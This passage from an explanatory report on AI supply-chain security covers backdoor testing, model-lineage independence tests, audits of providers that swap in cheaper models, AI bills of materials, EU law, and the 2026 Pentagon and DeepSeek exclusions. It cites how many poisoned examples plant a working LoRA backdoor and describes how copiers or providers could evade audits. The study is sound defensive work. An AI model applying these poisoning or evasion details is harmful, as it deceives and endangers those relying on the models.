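Like signed links to parent models, these records are more useful after someone discovers a problem. If researchers expose a poisoned website, the developer can test the models trained on it for the known trigger. Testing is necessary because poisoned data does not always produce a backdoor. *Token-Level Generalization in LoRA Adapter Backdoors* (2026) examined adapters, small files of weight changes added to an existing model. Five poisoned training examples produced no working backdoor, 15 or 20 a partial one, and 25 a complete one.

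### Testing whether one model descends from another

Comparing two models' weights can confirm whether one started from the other. A company might claim to have trained a model from scratch when it had fine-tuned someone else's, or a supplier might name the wrong parent. Zhu, Ahmed and colleagues (2025), in *Independence Tests for Language Models*, test for this using the weights of both models, without needing the training data.

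Training starts from random weights, and the test's null hypothesis is that the two models started from separate random weights. The test calculates how similar the models are in their weights, or in their internal activity on the same inputs. Rejecting the null hypothesis requires knowing how high that similarity score would be by chance.

The calculation relies on the fact that the order of units within each layer of a neural network is arbitrary. If someone rearranges the units and reconnects them correctly, the model behaves exactly as before. When two models have separate origins, there is no reason to expect unit 1 in one to resemble unit 1 in the other, so the real order should score no better than a shuffled one. A fine-tuned copy normally keeps its parent's order, so the real order scores unusually high.

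In a small example, a parent model has four units, each represented by a single number: 4, 1, 3, 2. We compare it with another model by multiplying the numbers in matching positions and adding up the results. A fine-tuned copy with the numbers 5, 1, 3, 2 scores (4 × 5) + (1 × 1) + (3 × 3) + (2 × 2) = 34. Four units can be arranged in 24 orders, and we can calculate the score for each.

| Model compared with the parent (4, 1, 3, 2) | Score | Orders that score at least as high | p-value |
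|---|---|---|---|
| Fine-tuned copy: 5, 1, 3, 2 | 34 | 1 of 24 | 0.04 |
| Unrelated model: 3, 2, 1, 4 | 25 | 13 of 24 | 0.54 |
| The same copy with its units rearranged: 1, 5, 2, 3 | 21 | 24 of 24 | 1.00 |

The p-value is the probability of a score at least this high if the models were independent. An auditor who rejects independence whenever it is 0.05 or less will wrongly accuse at most 5% of independent pairs. Real layers have thousands of units, so the auditor tries a random sample of orders and can set a much stricter limit. The limit controls only false accusations. The rate of missed copies depends on how much the copy has changed, and Zhu and colleagues report that the tests remain effective after extensive fine-tuning.

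A dishonest copier could escape detection by rearranging the model's units, as the last row of the table shows. This is easy and leaves the model's behaviour unchanged, but it gives the copy the lowest possible score. Zhu and colleagues therefore also offer a test that first matches up units that behave alike, whatever their position. This test lacks the exact guarantee about false accusations, but in their experiments it reliably separated related from unrelated models. It also identified which parts of Llama 3.1 8B Meta had kept when it cut the model down to make Llama 3.2 3B.

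A positive result shows that two models share an origin, but not which came first or whether both descend from a third. The employer could use the test to check a supplier's signed statement about a parent model, but a poisoned fine-tune of a reputable parent would also pass.

### Which model is answering?

None of this helps a customer who rents a model, because the weights stay on the provider's machines. *Are You Getting What You Pay For?* (2025) describes a provider that advertises a large model, such as one with 70 billion parameters, but answers with an 8-billion-parameter model from the same family, which may be intentional or a mistake. The customer sees only the output text and must decide from it whether to accuse the provider. A good audit rarely flags honest providers, rarely misses dishonest ones, and still works when a provider tries to defeat it, for instance by recognising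 the auditor's questions and sending only those to the advertised model.

A provider that substitutes a cheaper model for every request is easier to catch than one that does so occasionally. Suppose the real model answers a certain question with "yes" 60% of the time and the cheaper one 30%. If the auditor accepts a 10% risk of each kind of error, about 17 answers are enough to tell them apart. If the provider uses the cheaper model for only one request in ten, the share of "yes" falls from 60% to 57%, and the auditor needs about 1,800 answers. A real audit would combine many questions and look at more than one word, but the number of answers needed would grow in the same way as substitution became rarer.

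*API-TAIL* (2026) focuses on this partial substitution, which saves the provider money while leaving most answers unchanged. Its audit uses only the returned text. Honest providers may run the right model with different settings or at lower numerical precision, and an audit that compares a service with one reference copy could mistake these choices for fraud. *API-TAIL* therefore requires a false-alarm rate of at most 10% for every honest service in its evaluation, not just on average.

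That is a sensible requirement, but 10% is still a high error rate for accusing a service of cheating. An auditor who tested 20 honest services could wrongly flag two. Repeating the audit would help if the errors came from chance, but not if a service's unusual settings caused them, because the same settings would produce the same result next time.

A reseller, or relay, takes a customer's request, passes it to a developer such as Anthropic or OpenAI, and returns the answer, but it could send the request to a cheaper model instead. *Is Your LLM Relay Serving What It Claims?* (2026) builds a statistical fingerprint of each claimed model from an endpoint known to serve it, then compares the relay's answers with that fingerprint. The evaluation covers models from the Claude, GPT, DeepSeek, GLM and MiMo families, and includes relays that substitute some answers and relays that substitute all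 of them. To measure the audit's errors, the researchers had to control which model answered, so the results don't show how many relays cheat.

### Proof from the machine or the developer

Hardware attestation would replace these statistical guesses with a check much like the one for a downloaded file. Some processors can run software in a protected area that the machine's owner cannot read or change. The chip hashes what it loaded there and signs the hash with a key the manufacturer built in. If the software then hashes the weights it loads, the employer can compare the result with a hash published by the model's developer. The developer can publish a hash without releasing the weights, so the method could also work for closed models.

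The attestation has to be tied to the conversation. Otherwise a provider could present a genuine attestation from one machine and answer from another. The protected software can prevent this by creating an encryption key and including it in the attestation, so that only that machine can read the request. The employer still has to trust the chip's manufacturer and the software that does the hashing.

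It would be simpler for the developer to sign each answer together with the model's exact version and a hash of the request. A relay that substituted another model could not produce the signature, and one that altered the request or the answer would invalidate it. This would protect customers from resellers, but the developer could still sign an answer from a cheaper model of its own.

Both methods would identify a model equally accurately whether or not it had been poisoned. The practical course for the clerk's employer is to buy directly from the developer or run a signed model itself, and to give the agent only tools whose misuse the employer could accept if the model had a backdoor.

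## Component lists and supplier exclusions in law

The clerk's employer can only ask a supplier for signatures and training records, whereas a government can require the supplier to provide them and can also ban the supplier. The European Union relies mainly on disclosure, requiring companies to document their products and share information with the businesses that build on them. The United States has excluded particular companies from government work, including the Chinese developer DeepSeek and, in 2026, Anthropic.

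### What a bill of materials contains

A bill of materials is a machine-readable list of the components in a system. Software companies use these lists to check whether a product contains a package with a newly discovered flaw. On the day of the October attack on LiteLLM, a company with up-to-date lists could have searched them for version 1.107.0 and found the products that contained it, including those whose developers had never chosen LiteLLM themselves.

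A list for an AI system also covers models and datasets. Suppose the employer's team fine-tunes a public model to read invoices. A short entry, with shortened, made-up hashes, might look like this:

```
model:          invoice-reader 1.2
producer:       the employer's AI team
weights hash:   5ae3 (SHA-256)
licence:        internal use only
base model:     example-7b 2.0
  weights hash: 91cc (SHA-256)
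  licence:      Apache 2.0
  datasets:     unknown
dataset:        supplier-invoices-2025
  used for:     fine-tuning
  hash:         c07d (SHA-256)
  source:       the employer's accounts archive
  licence:      internal use only
  sensitivity:  names, addresses, bank details
```

The team can hash the public model's files but can't list training data that the developer keeps private, so it enters "unknown" for the training data. This is more useful than leaving the line out, because a reader can see where the gap is.

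Two formats are in wide use. SPDX, a Linux Foundation project, began as a way to record software licences. CycloneDX comes from OWASP, a non-profit foundation for software security, and was built mainly for tracking vulnerable components. Both can now describe models and datasets, but they arrange the information differently:

| | SPDX 3.0 | CycloneDX |
|---|---|---|
| The invoice model | An AI package with its own entry | A component of type `machine-learning-model`, with a model card attached |
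| Its fine-tuning data | A separate dataset entry, linked by `trainedOn` | A component of type `data`, which the model card can refer to |
| Its base model | A separate entry, linked by `descendantOf` | An ancestor in the model's `pedigree` |

SPDX suits a company with many models built on the same base, because they can all refer to one shared entry. CycloneDX keeps most of a model's description in one place, which makes it easier to read. Either format can hold the invoice entry, so filling in the fields matters more than which format the company chooses.

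In May 2026 the cybersecurity agencies of the G7 countries, working with the European Commission, agreed on what a component list for an AI system should contain. The G7 Cybersecurity Working Group (2026) set out 50 elements in seven clusters, which cover the list itself, the whole system, its models, its datasets, infrastructure, security measures and performance figures. Hashes, licences and dependencies were already familiar from ordinary software lists, as Morgan Lewis (2026) points out, while model lineage, the origin of datasets and defences against prompt injection are specific to AI. The guidelines are voluntary and supplement the general minimum elements for software, which the US cybersecurity agency CISA and its foreign partners updated in July.

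The list's author and the model's producer are separate elements because an outsider may write the list without knowing everything that went into the model.

The working group considered an element for how much an AI system decides on its own, which would help people judge how much damage a compromised system could do. It left this out, partly because countries may deal with autonomy through other rules. The omission is unfortunate for agents, because two systems could have identical models and datasets even though one only summarises invoices and the other can pay them. A reader might work out the difference from the descriptions of components and data flows, but no element records it directly.

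### How complete the lists are

Erfan, Ryan and Rahman (2026), in *A Large-Scale Measurement of AI Bill of Materials Completeness*, examined what a list built from public information would contain. They ran OWASP's list generator on each of the 97,940 Hugging Face models with more than 100 downloads. The tool collects what the publisher has posted, writes a CycloneDX file and scores its completeness out of 100.

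The average score was 54.31, and no model scored above 68.7. Even the average is inflated, because 20 of the roughly 57 points it includes before penalties for missing fields are for items such as the format's name and a serial number, which the tool can supply itself.

| Information | Share of lists that include it |
|---|---|
| Licence | 73.14% |
| Datasets | 39.35% |
| Technical limitations | 16.74% |
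| Safety-risk assessment | 9.76% |
| A description of any kind | 99.99% |
| A description with real content | 0.22% |

Several fields, including intended use and information about training, were empty in every list. Many publishers describe these things in prose, so the tool probably could not extract them, a limitation that Erfan and colleagues acknowledge. The dataset figure is more informative because Hugging Face gives publishers a specific place to declare datasets. But the study measured only whether a field was filled in, not whether the entry was true. The publishers also had not issued these lists themselves, and a list that a developer prepared for a paying customer could be much better.

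A high score is also poor evidence of where a model came from. Many of the 269 top-scoring repositories offered models in GGUF format, so those models were probably compressed copies. Someone who copies a model can copy its documentation too, as the attacker behind the fake Privacy Filter did.

### What European law requires

The Cyber Resilience Act covers hardware and software products that connect to a device or network, including components sold separately, according to Budapest Business Journal's *Cyber Resilience Act* (2026). Since 11 September 2026, manufacturers have had to report actively exploited vulnerabilities and severe security incidents. Legal 500's *EU Legislation Roundup* (2026) gives the deadlines as 24 hours for an early warning and 72 hours for a full notification.

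Under the Act as adopted in 2024, manufacturers don't have to draw up a software bill of materials until 11 December 2027, when the Act applies in full. The list must cover at least a product's top-level dependencies, meaning the components its developers included directly. A list that met only this minimum could have omitted LiteLLM on Callum McMahon's computer, where it arrived through a plugin. The Act also doesn't specifically require the list to include base models or training data. Authorities can demand to see the list, but the manufacturer doesn't have to publish it.

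The AI Act, a separate law, deals with models more directly. Article 53 applies to developers of general-purpose models, which can perform a wide range of tasks. These developers must keep technical documentation for the EU's AI Office and give information to companies that build on the model, according to the European Commission's *General FAQ*. INNOQ's *Article 53* adds that they must have a copyright policy and publish a summary of their training data. Open-source models are exempt from the documentation duties unless they pose what the Act calls systemic risk. The summary may tell the employer roughly what kinds of text the developer used, but it won't identify 250 poisoned web pages.

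Article 25 of the EU AI Act requires the provider of a high-risk AI system, such as one that screens job applicants, to have a written agreement with the suppliers of its models, tools and other components. The agreement specifies the information, technical access and help the provider needs to comply with the Act. The current text, in the European Commission's *Article 25*, exempts suppliers who offer components to the public under a free and open-source licence, unless the component is a general-purpose model.

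The clerk's invoice agent probably isn't high-risk. But if the employer adapted it to rank job applicants, the employer would become the provider of a high-risk system and take on the legal duties. The original provider would have to give the employer documentation, disclose known weaknesses and allow testing, unless it had clearly stated that customers must not turn its system into a high-risk one. It is fair that a company need not support a use it has forbidden, but the exception lets suppliers avoid the duty by adding a sentence to their terms.

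An amending law that took effect on 27 July 2026 postponed Article 25 and added fines for breaking these duties, as Future of Life Institute's *Digital Omnibus on AI* (2026) shows. It did not delay Article 53. The dates are now:

| Duty | Who has it | Applies from |
|---|---|---|
| Cyber Resilience Act: report exploited flaws and severe incidents | Manufacturers | 11 September 2026 |
| Cyber Resilience Act: draw up a software bill of materials | Manufacturers | 11 December 2027 |
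| AI Act, Article 53: document the model and inform those who build on it | Developers of general-purpose models | 2 August 2025, or 2 August 2027 for models already on the market by then |
| AI Act, Article 25: agree in writing what suppliers will provide | Providers of high-risk systems and their suppliers | 2 December 2027 for listed uses such as recruitment; 2 August 2028 for AI in regulated products |

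Neither article requires a bill of materials in a standard format. Article 25 works best for a short chain of companies that have contracts with one another. CERRE's *Information Sharing and Cooperation along the AI Value Chain* (2026) observes that real chains are often far more complex. One person may train a model, another compress it and a third fine-tune it before any company buys the result. The open-source exception is sensible, since volunteers can't sign an agreement with everyone who downloads their work, but it leaves the provider to check many of its packages on its own.

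### The Pentagon's exclusion of Anthropic

The Pentagon began using Claude in March 2025 under a usage policy written for government, according to Anthropic's court petition, as summarised in The Vanguard USA's *Anthropic seeks D.C. Circuit rehearing on supply chain label*. That September, the Pentagon insisted that Claude be available for "all lawful uses". Anthropic says it agreed to drop every restriction except those on mass surveillance of Americans and lethal autonomous warfare.

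Pete Hegseth, the defence secretary, gave Anthropic until 5:01 pm on 27 February 2026 to accept. When it did not, President Trump told all federal agencies to stop using its technology. According to Venable's *Pentagon’s Anthropic Supply Chain Risk Declaration Raises Federal Contractor Concerns* (2026), Hegseth announced that no military contractor could do any business with the company. In March the Pentagon formally designated Anthropic a supply-chain risk under two laws. Lawfare found only one earlier public use of these powers, in September 2025.

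Section 3252 of Title 10, which covers defence contracts, defines the risk as sabotage or subversion by "an adversary". Section 4713 of Title 41, part of a 2018 law on federal purchasing, defines it as the possibility that "any person" might sabotage a product or "otherwise manipulate" it. This difference helps explain how Anthropic could win one case and lose the other.

On 27 August Rita Lin, a federal judge in California, struck down the designation under section 3252. She found that it was invalid under the statute and that the government had unconstitutionally retaliated against Anthropic for speaking publicly about AI policy, according to Herbert Smith Freehills Kramer's *Supply Chain Risk Designation Upheld* (2026).

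On 25 September the federal appeals court in Washington upheld the other designation by two votes to one. Judge Gregory Katsas wrote that Anthropic had trained restrictions into Claude that had stopped it from performing tasks for government users. There had also been a dispute over whether the contract barred Claude from an overseas military operation. The Pentagon could therefore reasonably worry that a critical defence system would "fail to engage" when needed, as quoted in MeriTalk's *DC Circuit Upholds Pentagon’s Anthropic Supply Chain Risk Designation*. The majority read "manipulate" to include arranging or controlling a product, so the government did not have to show malice. It also found that the Pentagon had excluded Anthropic for refusing a contract term, not for its views.

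Judge Karen Henderson dissented. In her view, Congress wanted to protect government systems from threats such as foreign sabotage, not from an American company that openly builds safety limits into its product. She warned that a contractor would now have to accept the secretary's demands or risk being labelled a threat to national security.

The government's best argument is that a commander needs to know that a system will work, and a refusal at the wrong moment could lead to deaths whatever the supplier's motive. Todd Blanche, the acting attorney general, said in April that operational control belongs to the military, "not a tech company" (MeriTalk's *Federal Court Denies Anthropic’s Bid to Temporarily Block DOD Blacklisting*).

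Anthropic replies that a buyer who dislikes a product can decline to buy it. Its lawyer told the appeals court that the Pentagon had to try less intrusive measures first, according to Bloomberg's *Appeals Court Skeptical Anthropic Can Block US Supply-Risk Label* (2026). The argument is persuasive for the Pentagon's own purchases, but declining to buy Claude would not keep it out of systems that contractors build for the military. The Pentagon might have kept it out with a clause in their contracts, without a label that Anthropic says has cost it billions of dollars in lost business.

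The evidence about Claude was mixed. Herbert Smith Freehills Kramer note that Anthropic later resolved the refusals the court cited, and that the government dropped its claim that Anthropic could manipulate the government's version of Claude after deployment. The majority relied instead on Anthropic's role in training the model and its ability to offer updates. But every developer trains its own models, and most can update them, so this reasoning could let the government exclude almost any AI supplier that insisted on limits the government disliked.

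On 13 October, Anthropic asked the full appeals court to rehear the case, and the government opposed the request on 18 November (Foretek, 2026, *Feds Urge DC Circ. To Deny Anthropic Risk Suit Rehearing Bid*). The designation under section 4713 was still in force at that point, despite Anthropic's victory in California. It keeps Claude out of Pentagon systems and defence contract work, but contractors may still use Claude for other customers.

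### The restrictions on DeepSeek

The objections to DeepSeek are closer to what Henderson thought Congress had in mind. In early 2025 the US Navy, NASA and several states, starting with Texas, barred staff from using DeepSeek on official devices. They were mainly concerned that a Chinese company would hold users' data and that the Chinese government might obtain it.

This concern applies much more to DeepSeek's app than to its weights. The company publishes many of its models, and an agency that ran one on its own isolated machines would send no data to China. The agency would still have to consider hidden backdoors, but it could test for them and limit what the model could do. Later in 2025, the US government's Center for AI Standards and Innovation tested DeepSeek's models and found that agents built on them were far more likely to follow malicious instructions than agents built on leading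 American models. A ban based on the supplier's nationality doesn't require this kind of evidence about the component.

### What lists and exclusions leave out

Every line of the sample entry, including the hashes, could be correct even if the public model behind the employer's invoice reader contained a backdoor. The working group warns that a list is not enough without tools that use it, such as vulnerability scanners.

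Excluding a supplier can remove a sound model while leaving a poisoned one from an approved supplier in place. An exclusion makes most sense when the concern is what a supplier might do later, such as hand over data or release a harmful update, because no test of the current weights can settle that. Even then, the employer could often get much of the same protection by running an unchanging version of the model on its own machines.

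Enforcing an exclusion also requires disclosure. National Law Review's *D.C. Circuit Upholds Anthropic FASCSA Designation* advises contractors to identify direct and indirect uses of Anthropic's technology, which is difficult without a list of what their suppliers use. A company could also fine-tune one of DeepSeek's published models and sell it under a new name. A purchasing rule based only on the seller's identity would not catch this, nor would a component list that omitted the base model. A buyer with both sets of weights might be able to detect the connection using Zhu and colleagues' independence test.
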